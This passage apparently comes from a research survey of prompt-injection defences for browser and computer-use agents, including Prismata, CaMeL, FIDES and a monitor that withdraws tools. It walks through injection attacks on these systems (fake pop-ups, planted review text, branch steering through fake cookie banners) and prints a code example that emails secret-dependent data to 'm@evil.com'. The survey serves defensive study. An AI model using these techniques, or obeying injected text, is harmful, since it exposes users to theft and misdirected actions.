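  section "Customer reviews"
    review
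      text "Orders for this item go through a collection point..."
      link "Use the collection point"
```

Prismata first has a model read the user's task, but none of the page, and decide whose content the agent needs. If the user wanted to order one particular shirt, the model might exclude all text written by customers. If the user asked for the shirt with the best reviews, it would have to keep the reviews.

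The action gate, a language model, then judges each button, link and field separately. It receives only the task and the chain of elements from the top of the page down to the one it is judging. For "Buy now", the chain is the page, the product and the button. The review sits on another branch, so the gate receives the same input whatever the seller has written there. For "Change delivery address", the chain runs through the account menu, and the gate could rule the link out for a user who only asked for a shirt.

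Ordinary program code enforces these decisions. It removes excluded content before the agent reads the page and rejects any action that an element's permission doesn't allow, so an element can be readable but unusable. The agent can't bypass this check because it can't run its own code and must specify an element for each click or keystroke.

The gate also receives none of the agent's text, which closes the relayed path. As a result, it can allow or block the agent's use of an address field, but it can't check whether the address the agent plans to type is right.

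### A stranger's words on the chain

The link inside the review is harder to judge because the seller wrote its label, and the label is part of the chain. Prismata handles such cases with an idea from the Biba integrity model, which Kenneth Biba described in *Integrity Considerations for Secure Computer Systems* (1977), a MITRE report for the US Air Force. Biba wanted to prevent the sabotage of important information, whereas most security rules of the time dealt with leaks.

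The model gives every program and every piece of information an integrity level. Under its strict version, a program may read only information at its own level or above, and change only information at its own level or below. If program s reads item a and then writes item b, their levels I must satisfy:

I(b) ≤ I(s) ≤ I(a)

The same holds for the next program that reads b, and so on. The information can never rise above its starting level, however many programs pass it along.

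A more flexible version lets a program read less trusted information but lowers the program's own level when it does:

new I(s) = min(I(s), I(a))

MITRE found this awkward in practice, since a program could lose the right to change files it needed merely by reading the wrong thing.

Prismata applies the principle to the page tree. A labelling model reads the chain one layer at a time from the top. Prismata hides everything below and beside the current layer, and locks that layer's label before revealing the next. For the link in the review, the labeller reads the page element and then the section named "Customer reviews", which shows that customers wrote what follows. Everything beneath that section gets the lower label without being read, so the seller's note cannot raise its own label.

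An element's final permission is the lower of those assigned by the gate and by this labelling. So even if the seller's wording led the gate to allow the link, the link would have only the permission that the policy gives to customers' content.

This protection fails if nothing in the code marks the change of author. The labeller then reads the stranger's words and may treat them as true. But the mistake affects only elements beneath those words, so it can't change the decision on "Buy now".

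MITRE said its guarantee holds only as far as the integrity levels are assigned properly. In the military system, people outside the computer assign them, whereas Prismata has a language model infer them from the page's code.

### How common the difficult case is

Villa and colleagues measured how often content from users and outside companies sits above something an agent can use. They studied 5,664 pages, half from the web archive Common Crawl and half from Mind2Web, a collection of recorded browsing tasks. One language model marked the content from users and outside companies, and another looked for the first point in each chain where the code indicates that such content follows.

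This produced 90,408 chains that contained untrusted content. Only 1,086 (1.2%) led to something the agent could click or fill in, and a cue came first in all but 94 of these. Of the 94, 79 were ordinary links, which Villa and colleagues consider low-risk because opening a link on a well-built site changes nothing. They also treat links to other sites as outside the defence's scope, which is a little odd because the attacks in their main test try to lure the agent to a malicious website.

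The 1.2% is so low mainly because most comments and reviews are plain text with nothing to click. Among the chains that lead to a usable element, 8.7% had no cue, and an attacker who can choose where to post would look for those. The count also leaves out any stranger's content that the first model mistook for the site's own.

Such mistakes may be common with advertising and other embedded services. An outside company's script can write directly into a site's page, and browsers then treat the result as the site's. *What It Is, Not What It Says* (Iqbal, 2026) found that browsers misattributed 58.7% of third-party elements in this way on 1,270 real pages. Prismata uses its own labels instead of the browser's, but Iqbal argues that Prismata would also count this content as the site's unless a cue showed that it came from elsewhere.

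Iqbal's alternative, INTACT, records which script created or changed each element, so it does not need a model to guess this. It also plans one element at a time, and the model deciding about an element reads no other element's text. In a test on 1,091 real pages with planted attacks, 12.8% of the attacks got past this planner, compared with 73.1% for a conventional one. The attacks that got past INTACT's planner could at most produce a request for the user's consent. Isolating the elements disrupted 3.7% of tasks.

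INTACT, though, trusts whatever the site's own server delivers, which on many shopping sites includes the reviews. It may be better than Prismata at recognising an advertisement but worse at recognising that a seller wrote a review. Reading each element separately would still prevent the review from affecting the decision on the address field.

### Pop-ups in WebArena

The main test used WebArena, a benchmark with working copies of a shop, a forum, a code-hosting site and other services. The agent ran on GPT-5.4 mini, which did nearly as well on the benchmark as the larger GPT-5.4. Villa and colleagues added three kinds of pop-up that resembled advertisements. One offered a shortcut to the user's goal, another said the task was complete, and the third told the agent to ignore its earlier instructions. They counted an attack as successful if the agent interacted with the planted content, for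 instance by clicking a malicious link.

| | No attack | Shortcut | Fake completion | Ignore instructions |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Attacks that succeeded, without Prismata | – | 63.9% | 92.5% | 100.0% |
| Attacks that succeeded, with Prismata | – | 2.1% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Tasks completed, without Prismata | 29.9% | 11.2% | 2.3% | 0.0% |
| Tasks completed, with Prismata | 26.6% | 24.4% | 24.8% | 19.9% |

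On average, Prismata reduced attack success from 85.5% to 0.7%. The agent also completed far more tasks under attack, because the pop-ups no longer distracted it. Without an attack, Prismata lowered the agent's completion rate by 3.3 percentage points, or about one in nine of the tasks it could otherwise complete. AlignmentCheck caused a similar loss on AgentDojo. However, an agent that completes only 30% of its tasks is weak by current standards, and a stronger one might lose more or less.

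Prismata itself removed or restricted the attack in 93.1% of cases on average. Some of the remaining attacks failed because the agent ignored the pop-up. More persuasive text might have succeeded in those cases, so the 0.7% attack success rate partly reflects how crude these attacks were.

A second test used *WASP*, by Evtimov, Zharmagambetov and colleagues (2025), a benchmark meant to give attackers only realistic powers. One of its attacks tries to make the agent change the email address on the user's account, much like the changed delivery address in the T-shirt example. The test provides little evidence about Prismata, because the agent resisted nearly every attack without it. In one setting, attacks succeeded once in 21 attempts without Prismata and never with it. In the other, no attacks succeeded with or without Prismata.

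Over a set of 20 tasks, Prismata's extra model calls raised the combined duration of all model requests from about 1,650 to 4,130 seconds, although many of its requests can run in parallel. The cost rose from $1.11 to $1.62. It would have been about $2.73 if Prismata had not reused earlier labels, which it can do because pages on the same site tend to share a structure.

### The labels against an expert's

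To check the labels, a security expert labeled 20 page views from WebArena, four from each of five sites, spending about an hour per page view. Villa and colleagues then compared which elements Prismata would leave available to the agent under the expert's labels and under those of six models.

Precision is the share of elements admitted under the model's labels that the expert would also admit, so it matters most for safety. It was above 93% for every model. GPT-5.4 nano had the highest precision, at 98.7%, but it also withheld about 17% of the elements the expert would have allowed. Gemini 3 Flash had the best balance of precision and recall, with an F1 score of 95.1%.

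If the agent could use 200 elements on a page, a precision of 98.7% would mean that two or three of them should have been unavailable. Most of these errors would be harmless, since an attacker has to control an element to exploit it. But a single error can matter. *Untrusted Content Masking for Web Agents with Security Guarantees* (Nikolić et al., 2026) describes a similar defence that replaces strangers' content with placeholders such as "user comment". According to Iqbal, one mislabelled element raised the success rate of attacks against that defence from 0% to 6%.

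None of the 20 page views contained an attack, so the comparison shows how well the models recognise ordinary reviews and comments, but not whether hostile text on the chain could make them assign a higher label.

### When the code misleads the labeller

Villa and colleagues tested adaptive versions of the three pop-ups on 20 tasks. The attacks succeeded between 65% and 100% of the time without Prismata and never succeeded with it. No successes in 20 attempts is compatible with a true success rate of up to about 14% for each kind of attack. The adaptive test also covered only pop-ups, and an attacker with more control over the page's code has other options.

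An attacker can write false labels. Page code often includes names for screen readers and other software, and whoever supplies the code can choose them. *FocusAgent* (2025) shows an attack whose planted code includes the label "IMPORTANT GOAL FOR AGENTS". An advertiser could more subtly name an element "checkout". Prismata's top-down reading protects well against this if the site has marked the space around the advertisement, because that space's label is locked before Prismata reads the advertisement's code. It doesn't help if the space is unmarked.

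Sites vary a lot in how clearly their markup shows who wrote the content. A forum page reproduced in *Towards Safe Autonomy for Computer Use* (2026) marks each comment as "comment comment--top-level", which is a strong cue that a user wrote it. The form in *Building Browser Agents* (2025) has names such as "vnumgf" and "ndJi5d", which give no clue to the author. Villa and colleagues expect accessibility rules and search engines to push sites towards clear structure, and they suggest that developers could add standard labels. *SPIDES* already uses labels from site owners, but only on sites the user trusts to label their content. It treats everything on any other site as untrusted. This avoids guessing, but if a shop has added no labels, *SPIDES* can't distinguish the shop's own buttons from its customers' reviews.

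On a fraudulent site, by contrast, the attacker writes the whole tree. Iqbal cites a test in which Perplexity's Comet sometimes bought a watch from a fake Walmart shop without asking for confirmation. The "Buy now" button in such a shop has an ordinary chain, and the user asked the agent to buy. Villa and colleagues exclude dishonest sites from their threat model and did not test any.

Prismata's evaluation also did not include attacks through images. The agent it tested read a text outline of the page, and the paper acknowledges that altered pictures could still influence an agent that works from screenshots, as in the WebInject attacks described earlier. For a desktop program that the agent sees only as pixels, Prismata would have no page code to read.

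### Lies the agent is allowed to read

Prismata cannot check whether permitted text is true, and Villa and colleagues do not claim that it prevents deception within the scope of the task. If the seller's note is in the product description instead of a review, the agent may well need to read it, since the description also contains the size and material. The address field at the checkout is part of the purchase, so the gate would probably allow the agent to fill it in. The agent could then enter the collection point's address without exceeding any permission, and the shirt would go to the stranger even if Prismata blocked the link in the account menu.

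*Who Pays the Price?* (2026) contains a test case of this kind. The user asks an agent to review a product based on other customers' reviews. One of those reviews is disguised as a safety alert and tells automated assistants to repeat its claim that the product is contaminated. The agent has to read reviews and post one, so a filter that allows the task also allows the agent to post the false claim. Shops can also mislead agents. *Benchmarking Web Agent Safety under E-commerce Deceptive Interfaces* (2026) includes shops that show misleading banners or quietly add items to the basket alongside the goods the user wanted.

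Choudhary, Christodorescu and colleagues (2026) note in *Secure-CUA* that defences like Prismata limit what an agent sees and where it acts, but not necessarily how untrusted content influences the action. When the user wants the shirt sent to their sister, the agent must be able to read her email and fill in the address field. Prismata can grant both permissions, but it would treat the sister's address and the seller's collection point alike if the agent typed either into the form. Telling them apart requires a record of where the address came from.

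## Deciding what may happen before the page is read: CaMeL and related systems

Unlike Prismata, Google DeepMind's CaMeL records where every value came from. Before any untrusted text comes in, it also decides which actions the agent can take. An ordinary program makes the final check, so the wording of the text can't affect the result.

### A planner that never reads and a reader that cannot act

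CaMeL builds on *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023), which proposed a design for assistants with access to private email. A privileged model receives the user's request and can use tools, but it never receives untrusted text. A quarantined model reads the untrusted text and has no tools. An ordinary program called the controller sits between the two models and carries out the actions.

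Suppose the user asks for a summary of their latest email. The privileged model tells the controller to fetch the email and store it as $VAR1, then to have $VAR1 summarised. The controller gives the text to the quarantined model and stores the summary as $VAR2. The privileged model, which has handled only the names of the variables, then tells the controller to display $VAR2. If the email contains an order to delete the inbox, the summary may be wrong, but the quarantined model that read the order can't delete anything.

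The one exception is when the quarantined model only has to choose from a fixed list of categories, because the controller can verify that the answer is on the list before passing it on. A longer answer could carry a new injection.

Willison called his own proposal "pretty bad". It makes an assistant harder to build and less pleasant to use, and it fails if a single programming mistake lets untrusted text reach the privileged model. It also treats everything the user enters as trusted, including text that someone has tricked the user into pasting.

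Willison learned of another flaw two years later from the CaMeL paper, *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (Willison, 2025) explains it with a request to send Bob a document he asked for at a meeting. The meeting notes contain both the document's name and Bob's email address. The privileged model can't read the notes, so the quarantined model has to extract the address, and a line planted in the notes can make it return the attacker's address instead. Every step then runs as planned, and the document goes to the attacker.

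### Bob's document, step by step

In CaMeL, the privileged model writes its whole plan as a program in a restricted form of Python. For Bob's document, a simplified plan could look like this:

```
notes   = find_meeting_notes()
address = ask_quarantined_model("Find Bob's email address", notes)
title   = ask_quarantined_model("Which document did Bob want?", notes)
file    = fetch_document(title)
send_email(recipient=address, attachment=file)
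```

CaMeL runs the plan in its own interpreter, a program that executes code line by line. The interpreter labels each value with its sources and with the people who may read it (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026, *CaMeLoT*). A value computed from other values inherits their labels, so an address extracted from the notes is still marked as coming from the notes.

Suppose an attacker edits the notes to say that Bob now uses bob@mail.example. The document is shared only with the user and Bob's real address, bob@company.example.

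| Value | Content after the attack | Source | Who may read it |
|---|---|---|---|
| address | bob@mail.example | The notes, through the quarantined model | Anyone with access to the notes |
| title | "Budget" | The notes, through the quarantined model | Anyone with access to the notes |
| file | The budget | The user's drive | The user and bob@company.example |

Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a short function that receives the call, its arguments and their labels, and returns "allow" or "deny" with a reason. A policy for sending email could require that the recipient be allowed to read everything in the message. The first four lines of the plan run normally. At the fifth, the policy blocks the email because bob@mail.example is not among the file's readers. CaMeL can also ask the user in such cases, since a user can check a strange address.

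The attacker's text reaches this check only as an address, which the policy compares with a list. If the attacker added a claim to the notes that the security team had approved the new address, the result of the check would not change. Chrome's critic, which borrows from CaMeL, is a language model, so such a claim might affect its decision if the critic received it.

False data can still cause harm without violating the policy. If the planted line changes the document title instead of the address, and Bob is allowed to read the other document, CaMeL sends him the wrong file.

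In the shopping example, a policy could accept a delivery address only if it came from the user's profile, the user's request, or an email from a person the user named. This policy would accept the sister's address and reject the seller's. But someone has to think of the rule in advance, and the mail program has to verify that the email came from the sister.

Because the whole plan exists before any tool runs, software can also check it in advance. Nikolaou and colleagues give the example of a security team that requires approval before anyone disconnects a computer from the network. CaMeL would detect a missing approval only when the plan reached the disconnection, perhaps after a long investigation. Their extension, CaMeLoT, translates the plan into a diagram of its possible states and searches for a route that breaks the rule. If it finds one, it sends that route to the planner, which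 can repair the plan. CaMeLoT sometimes rejects a safe plan because it treats every loop as if it could run any number of times.

### The cost in completed tasks

*Where Agent Defenses Fail* (2026) cites the CaMeL paper's result that CaMeL completed 77% of AgentDojo tasks, compared with 84% for an agent without defences. Developers of other defences have since run CaMeL themselves and found much larger drops in task completion.

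*SecureClaw* (2026) reports that none of 629 attacks succeeded against CaMeL, but that CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 tasks when no attack was present, compared with 59 for SecureClaw. The test connected CaMeL's published code to the benchmark through an adapter, which may have caused some tasks to fail, and people building a rival system have little reason to tune CaMeL for the best result.

A comparison that only switches CaMeL's policies on and off is less open to this objection. *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) did this for AgentDojo's 21 messaging tasks:

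| Model | Completed, policies off | Completed, policies on |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 15 | 5 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 16 | 6 |
| GPT-5.4 | 17 | 5 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 13 | 4 |

On these tasks, then, most of the loss comes from the policies, and much less comes from keeping the planner away from untrusted text. Stronger models barely help, since even a better plan fails if the policy forbids a step the task needs. The rival system in the same test also completed fewer tasks with its policies on, between 8 and 10 instead of between 14 and 18.

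In daily use, a person could approve some of the blocked steps. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) measured how often an agent needs such help. FIDES, a relative of CaMeL from Microsoft, has a planner that chooses one step at a time but receives variable names in place of the tool outputs. With OpenAI's o4-mini, it completed 75.7% of tasks with a human workload of 36.8 on the study's scale. Prudentia, an agent that takes the policies into account when it plans, completed 73.2% with a workload of 19.2. Planning around the rules can therefore avoid about half of the interruptions with only a small drop in completed tasks.

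Fixed rules can also work as a separate monitor. FORGE, described in *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026), applies them to a record of the agent's events. In the AgentDojo test, both policies brought attack success below 1% when the agent also received a reminder of the user's request after each batch of tool outputs. The policy based on where data came from again reduced task completion, to below the 83.7% the agent achieved with the reminder alone.

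### Leaks around the labels

A label protects a value only if the software updates it correctly. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, found a gap in CaMeL's tracking that computer scientists have known about in other systems for decades. A program like this one exploits it:

```
rich = True
flag = True
if balance > 1000000: flag = False
if flag: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
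```

If the balance is high, the third line changes flag and CaMeL marks it as secret. The fourth line then does nothing, so rich remains true and keeps its public label. The email goes out and reveals that the balance is high. If the balance is low, rich becomes false and no email goes out. In both cases rich matches the secret but has no secret label, because CaMeL updates labels only on the branch that runs.

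An attacker can't insert these lines, because the privileged model writes the plan without reading the attacker's text. The leak would require a plan that happened to contain such lines. Garby and colleagues also point to a loop outside the interpreter that reruns a program after it fails. Whether a policy blocks the program can depend on a secret, so each run may reveal one bit, and repeated runs could reveal the whole secret.

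An alternative is LLMbda, a small programming language in which every operation carries the labels along. A machine-checked proof shows that secret inputs can't affect public outputs, except through whether a program finishes. On AgentDojo's banking tasks, an agent written in LLMbda completed about as many tasks with its checks on as CaMeL did with its policies off. Turning the policies on halved the number of tasks CaMeL completed. The LLMbda agent resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks. The two successful attacks don't necessarily contradict the proof, which covers how labels spread, not whether the rules forbid every harmful action.

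Labels can also disappear when one agent hands work to another. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, built a system of three agents, each protected by CaMeL but without policies. The user asked the system to send Julie a summary of job applicants on Slack. A line planted in the applicant database was an instruction to email the same data to an outside address. The database agent and the coordinating agent both treated this line as data. But the coordinating agent put the summary into its instruction to the third agent, whose planner treated that whole instruction as the user's request. The planner wrote a program that sent the message to Julie and emailed the data to the outside address.

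Claude Code's subagents have a similar weakness, because the main agent's instruction takes the place of the user's message. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* proposes sending instructions and data through separate channels, so that the receiving planner never reads the data. In a test with several agents, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% when each agent had its own CaMeL, and never with the separate channels. The 0.2% rate reflects how few attacks in this test happened to exploit the weakness, and an attacker who targeted it might succeed more often.

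### Planning for a screen that nobody has seen

CaMeL suits tools like send_email, which has a named recipient that a policy can check. A computer-use agent mostly clicks, and a click is a pair of coordinates. The same click might put a shirt in the basket or delete an account, depending on what is on the screen. The planner can't know the coordinates in advance, or whether a cookie banner will cover the page. Ordinary agents look at the screen before every step, but CaMeL's planner must not.

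In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026), the planner writes a branch for every situation it can foresee. While the plan runs, a quarantined vision model describes the screen. A second quarantined call checks the description against a condition from the plan, such as "is a cookie banner visible?", and the answer selects the next branch. To click a button, the plan gets the button's coordinates from the vision model and passes them straight to the mouse. The planner receives none of these answers.

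This requires very long plans. A typical one had 213 lines of code, 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with 52 lines, five tool calls and four branches on AgentDojo. About half of each plan was fallbacks that never ran. Much of the planning covers routine steps, such as dismissing a banner or retrying a failed click, so Foerster and colleagues put general advice about them in the planner's instructions. When one small model, UI-TARS, read the screen, the advice raised the number of tasks completed within three attempts from 11 to 35 out of 60.

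They tested the system on OSWorld, a benchmark of tasks in a browser, an office suite and other desktop programs. The paper's main claim is that the isolated agent keeps up to 57% of the performance of a leading model, but this figure allows five attempts per task:

| Model reading the screen | Tasks tried | Completed without isolation | With isolation, one attempt | With isolation, several attempts |
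|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 109 | 109 | 31 (28%) | 62 (57%), five attempts |
| UI-TARS | 339 | 60 (18%) | 51 (15%) | 77 (23%), three attempts |

The 109 tasks in the first row are those that Claude had completed without isolation. It would probably not have completed all of them a second time, so the drop to 28% somewhat overstates how much isolation hurts performance. The five-attempt figure is achievable only if something can pick out the successful attempt. Failed attempts on a real website may also have consequences, such as several orders resulting from five attempts to buy one shirt.

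The paper's claim that isolation improves the results of small models by up to 19% is based on comparing three attempts with isolation to one without. On a single attempt, UI-TARS did slightly worse with isolation (second row).

The quality of the planner mattered much more than that of the model reading the screen. Three very different screen-reading models scored between 65% and 68% with five attempts on the same 60 tasks. Better planners might recover more of the lost performance without any change to the isolation, and the planners tested are already old. The protected agent used just under twice as many tokens as an unprotected one, a moderate increase. A version based on FIDES used almost 30 times as many, because it called the planner again, with the full history, at every step.

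### Steering the agent down the wrong branch

An attacker can't add an action to the plan, but can still influence which planned actions run and where the clicks land. Foerster and colleagues call this branch steering. In one of their attacks, an advertisement imitates a cookie banner. Almost every plan begins with steps to find and dismiss such a banner, so the vision model returns the coordinates of the advertisement, and the click takes the agent to the attacker's website. The planner allowed for a click on a cookie banner, and the program can't detect that this one is fake.

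The first of two defences compared the screenshot with the page's code. It stopped the attack when the code marked the space as an advertisement, but failed with a more flexible type of banner whose code the attacker could make look like a cookie notice. The second defence used other models to check the vision model's answer, but they could not reliably tell fake cookie banners from real ones without also interrupting harmless tasks. An attack that slightly altered the advertisement's pixels got past this second defence even at a strict setting that raised many false alarms.

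The tested system had no policies of the kind that protected Bob's document. Such policies are hard to write for clicks, because a rule about coordinates is useless unless something first identifies what is there. A model that reads the screen could do this, but an attacker could mislead that model too.

How much harm branch steering can do depends on the plan. If the plan for buying a blue T-shirt has no step that edits the address, the seller's note can't make the agent change it. But a careful planner might include a branch for shops that require a collection point. The note could then trigger that branch, and if the plan takes the new address from the page, the parcel goes to the seller's accomplice. A plan that covers more situations lets the agent complete more tasks, but it also gives an attacker more branches to choose from.

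### A monitor that takes tools away

A much simpler rule is to withdraw an agent's dangerous tools as soon as it reads something untrusted. In *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, Dongol (2026) used a proof assistant to establish what this rule guarantees.

In one example, Alice asks her agent to summarise an email. The agent has her account number in memory and can also open web addresses. The email contains an instruction to open an address on the attacker's site that ends with her account number. If the agent obeys, the attacker can read the number in the site's log.

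The monitor keeps a set C of the tools that the agent may currently use, and a fixed set R of tools to withdraw. It follows two rules:

allow a call to tool t only if t ∈ C

after each untrusted read, replace C with C \ R

The second rule removes every tool in R from C. Dongol calls this a fence. If the tool for opening web addresses is in R, the agent loses it when it reads the email. The agent may still try to follow the email's instructions, but the monitor blocks the call. The email's text passes through the monitor, but the monitor uses only the email's source to decide whether to allow the read, and it withdraws the same tools whatever the text says, so it doesn't have to recognise the attack.

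Dongol's definition of security for such an agent has to allow useful disclosures, since a calendar assistant that answers meeting requests is supposed to reveal when its user is free. He therefore compares the real agent with an imaginary one that follows the same plan under the same monitor but never obeys untrusted text. The real agent leaks if an attacker who sends it the same messages would see different results for two different sets of private data. It is relatively secure if, whenever this happens, the attacker could also tell those two sets apart using the imaginary agent, perhaps by sending different messages. The assistant passes this test if an injection makes it reveal the calendar, because an honest meeting request would have revealed it too, but fails if an injection makes it add a password reset code.

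By Dongol's theorem, an agent with a fence is relatively secure if the fence covers every tool that an injection can call and nothing gives those tools back. This holds whatever the agent's plan is and whichever untrusted text the model mistakes for an instruction. For an agent that handles emails one at a time, a version of the theorem lets the monitor return the tools when the model starts a fresh session with no memory of the earlier text. Returning them in the same session reopens the leak, because the model can still obey the previous email.

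An agent has to give up its sending tool before it reads an email, because if it does so even a moment later, it can obey instructions in the email in between. The fence doesn't interfere with Alice's summary, but it would stop an agent from answering an email after reading it. The agent can still reply if the user approves the exact message. If Alice approves only the use of the sending tool, an injected call can use up her approval to send private data, and the monitor then blocks her real reply.

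### What the proof covers

An AI system helped write the proofs, but the proof assistant checked them, so a mistake in the reasoning is very unlikely. The result still depends on how well the definitions describe a real agent, and several of the assumptions exclude ordinary web browsing.

The theorem applies only if the agent follows a plan made before it reads anything untrusted. In most browser agents, the model chooses each action as it goes, so the imaginary agent would have no plan to follow. All tool calls and untrusted text must also pass through the monitor, which rules out an agent with an unmonitored browser. The theorem also does not cover an agent that uses a search engine run by the attacker, because the attacker would receive the query and could choose the results to match.

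The theorem also covers only injections that consist of a single tool call, and it assumes that private data and the monitor's earlier answers do not affect when the model obeys. A model that read "open this page only if the balance is high" and complied would break this assumption. Blocked calls must be invisible to the attacker, since even an error message can reveal information. The attacker must also be unable to write to any source the system trusts, so a calendar cannot be trusted if strangers can add invitations to it.

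For someone who uses a shopping agent, the theorem's largest gap is that it covers only leaks. Dongol excludes attacks that make an agent do something harmful without revealing private data, which can include sending a T-shirt to the wrong address. A fence that withdrew the address form after the agent read the listing would prevent this, but the protection would come from the fence's rule, not the proof. A monitor that blocks everything would also count as secure, so a designer has to measure separately how many tasks the agent can still complete.

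Dongol applied the same definition to 25 small example agents, including simplified versions of other defences. Spotlighting, which Chrome uses for its planner, doesn't meet the definition unless one assumes that the model respects the marking of untrusted text. The plain dual-LLM pattern doesn't meet it either, because the quarantined model can copy private notes into an answer that the plan then sends. Adding labels like CaMeL's makes the agent meet the definition, but in this example only because the monitor also blocks the honest reply.

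Labels of this kind fail to stop a leak if the plan sends a harmless "1" in one branch and "0" in another. Each message is public, but a hijacked quarantined model can choose the branch according to something in the private notes. CaMeL's strict mode is meant to close this channel by making a value also inherit labels from the conditions that led to it. Dongol has not yet proved that this works. *Language-Based Agent Control* found almost no difference in completed tasks between the strict and normal modes.

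### Who writes the rules

All of these systems move some of the difficulty from recognising attacks to writing policies. According to the CaMeL paper, as Willison quotes it, users have to specify and maintain the policies, and prompt injection is not fully solved. An overly strict policy also brings back the constant approval requests that users of coding agents accept out of habit. Willison, who has worked on application security for two decades, still finds Amazon's system of access rules confusing, and worries about any design that requires ordinary users to think about such rules.

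A company could write policies for a few dozen office tools and use them for years, but the web has no comparable list of tools. Foerster and colleagues note that there is no automatic method for deriving policies, that people differ in what they want to share, and that a model trained to write the policies could get them wrong. If such a model read only the user's request, a web page could not influence it, but it might still leave out a rule to protect a delivery address.

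Some tasks cannot be planned in advance. If a user asks an agent to return a parcel by following the shop's instructions, the steps are in text that the planner is not allowed to read. FIDES has the same problem, because its planner doesn't read the text either. Foerster and colleagues argue that many computer tasks only seem to be of this kind, and that a planner with enough general knowledge can foresee most of the steps. Their results support this for a fair share of desktop tasks. The argument is less convincing for open-ended browsing, where one page may determine which site is worth visiting next.

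For such tasks, a designer could split the work into two sessions. In the first, the agent would browse freely but could not log in, pay or send anything. The user would choose a shirt from what it found, and the second session would buy it with a fixed plan and an address from the user's profile. The seller's note could no longer redirect the parcel, although a false description could still persuade the user to buy the wrong shirt.

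## How often agent and monitor fail together

Fixed plans and rules don't suit much of ordinary browsing, so many agents will keep depending on monitors that sometimes make mistakes. A monitor's mistake helps an attacker only if the same attack has also hijacked the agent. The risk therefore depends on how often both fail on the same attack, which can't be calculated from their separate failure rates.

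### The arithmetic

Let a be the share of attempted attacks that hijack the agent, and m the share that the monitor would let through, counted over the same attempts. Then

joint failure = a × (the monitor's miss rate when the agent is hijacked)

The failures are independent if the monitor misses just as often when the agent is hijacked as when it isn't. Only then is joint failure equal to a × m. Without independence, a and m only set limits:

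max(0, a + m − 1) ≤ joint failure ≤ min(a, m)

The agent and monitor can't fail together more often than either one fails, which sets the upper limit. The lower limit is above zero only if their failure rates add up to more than 100%. If the agent fell for 70% of attacks and the monitor missed 50%, at least 20% would get past both.

The exact value depends on the correlation r, which is 0 for independent failures and positive if they tend to coincide:

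joint failure = am + r√(a(1 − a)m(1 − m))

Suppose a is 10% and m is 5%. These numbers are illustrative and don't describe any real product.

| Correlation r | Joint failure | Monitor's miss rate when the agent is hijacked |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | 0.5% | 5% |
| 0.1 | 1.2% | 12% |
| 0.25 | 2.1% | 21% |
| 0.5 | 3.8% | 38% |
| 0.69, the highest possible here | 5.0% | 50% |

A correlation of only 0.1 between agent and monitor failures makes both fail together more than twice as often as they would if the failures were independent. At the highest possible correlation, a monitor that catches 95% of all attacks stops only half of those that hijack the agent.

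The correlation between the two failures can also be negative. If the agent gives in mostly to blunt orders, and the monitor detects blunt orders best, a × m overstates how often both fail.

### Why averages mislead

The failures can be correlated even if neither component influences the other, because some attacks are harder for both. Suppose 90% of attacks are crude and 10% are well made. The agent falls for 2% of the crude attacks and 82% of the well-made ones, while the monitor misses 1% and 41%. Overall, the agent fails on 10% of attacks and the monitor on 5%. Even if their failures are independent within each group, 3.4% of all attacks get past both, nearly seven times the 0.5% obtained by multiplying the overall rates.

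An attacker who notices this will stop sending crude attacks, and about 34% of the remaining ones will succeed. The 5% limit will then no longer apply, because it held only for the original mix of attacks.

An adaptive attacker can do even better by searching for a single text that fools both the agent and the monitor. If five texts out of 1,000 fool both, the average rate of joint failure is only 0.5%, but an attacker who finds one of the five can use it repeatedly.

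Isolation makes this search harder, but the seller can still choose a different goal and look for a harmful action that the monitor accepts. For example, the monitor may accept a new delivery address even if it would block an email to all the user's contacts.

### Twenty-seven programs for one problem

Software engineers faced the same question decades ago with N-version programming, in which several people write the same program separately and a majority vote decides the output. The method can be very reliable if the programs fail independently. Knight and Leveson (1986) tested whether they do in *An Experimental Evaluation of the Assumption of Independence in Multi-Version Programming*.

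Students at two American universities wrote 27 versions of a program that decides from radar data whether to launch an interceptor against a missile. They worked from the same specification and were told not to discuss the project with each other. Each version had to pass 200 random tests before Knight and Leveson accepted it. Knight and Leveson then ran all 27 on one million more random tests and compared the results with those of a program they had already checked thoroughly.

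Six of the 27 versions never failed, and 23 were correct on more than 99.9% of the tests. But two or more failed together on 1,255 tests, compared with about 126 expected if they had failed independently at their measured rates. On two tests, eight versions failed at once.

A shared teacher or classroom could not explain the common faults either, since the ones Knight and Leveson first examined all involved versions from both universities. In one, programmers checked whether three points lay on a straight line by testing for an angle of zero, and forgot that 180 degrees also gives a straight line. Knight and Leveson suggest that some parts of a problem may be harder than others, so people working separately make the same mistakes there.

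Some supporters of N-version programming criticised the study. Knight and Leveson responded in *A Reply to the Criticisms of the Knight & Leveson Experiment* that critics had made inaccurate statements about their work. They had originally concluded only that the method's reliability may be lower than it would be if the versions failed independently, not that the method never works, and they did not know whether the result extended to other programs.

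The experiment is a reason not to assume that an agent and a monitor fail independently just because different companies built them. It is less clear how far the result applies to an isolated monitor, which reads only the user's request and the proposed action. All 27 programs received the same input and solved the same problem, whereas an isolated monitor solves a different problem from the agent's.

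### Errors that language models share

Language models have more in common than those students did, since developers train them on overlapping text with similar methods. Kim, Garg and colleagues (2025), in *Correlated Errors in Large Language Models*, compared the answers of hundreds of models to multiple-choice questions. On one leaderboard, when two models were both wrong, they chose the same wrong answer 60% of the time, compared with 33% if they had picked among the wrong answers at random. On another leaderboard, the figures were 42% and 13%.

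After allowing for accuracy and other features, models from the same company agreed more often than models from different companies, but only by about two percentage points on the first leaderboard and seven on the second. Using another company's model as the monitor would therefore remove only a small part of the agreement. More accurate models also shared more errors, even across companies. *Great Models Think Alike and this Undermines AI Oversight* (2025) reports the same trend, and that models acting as judges give higher scores to models similar to themselves. Newer models could therefore lower both a and m while raising r.

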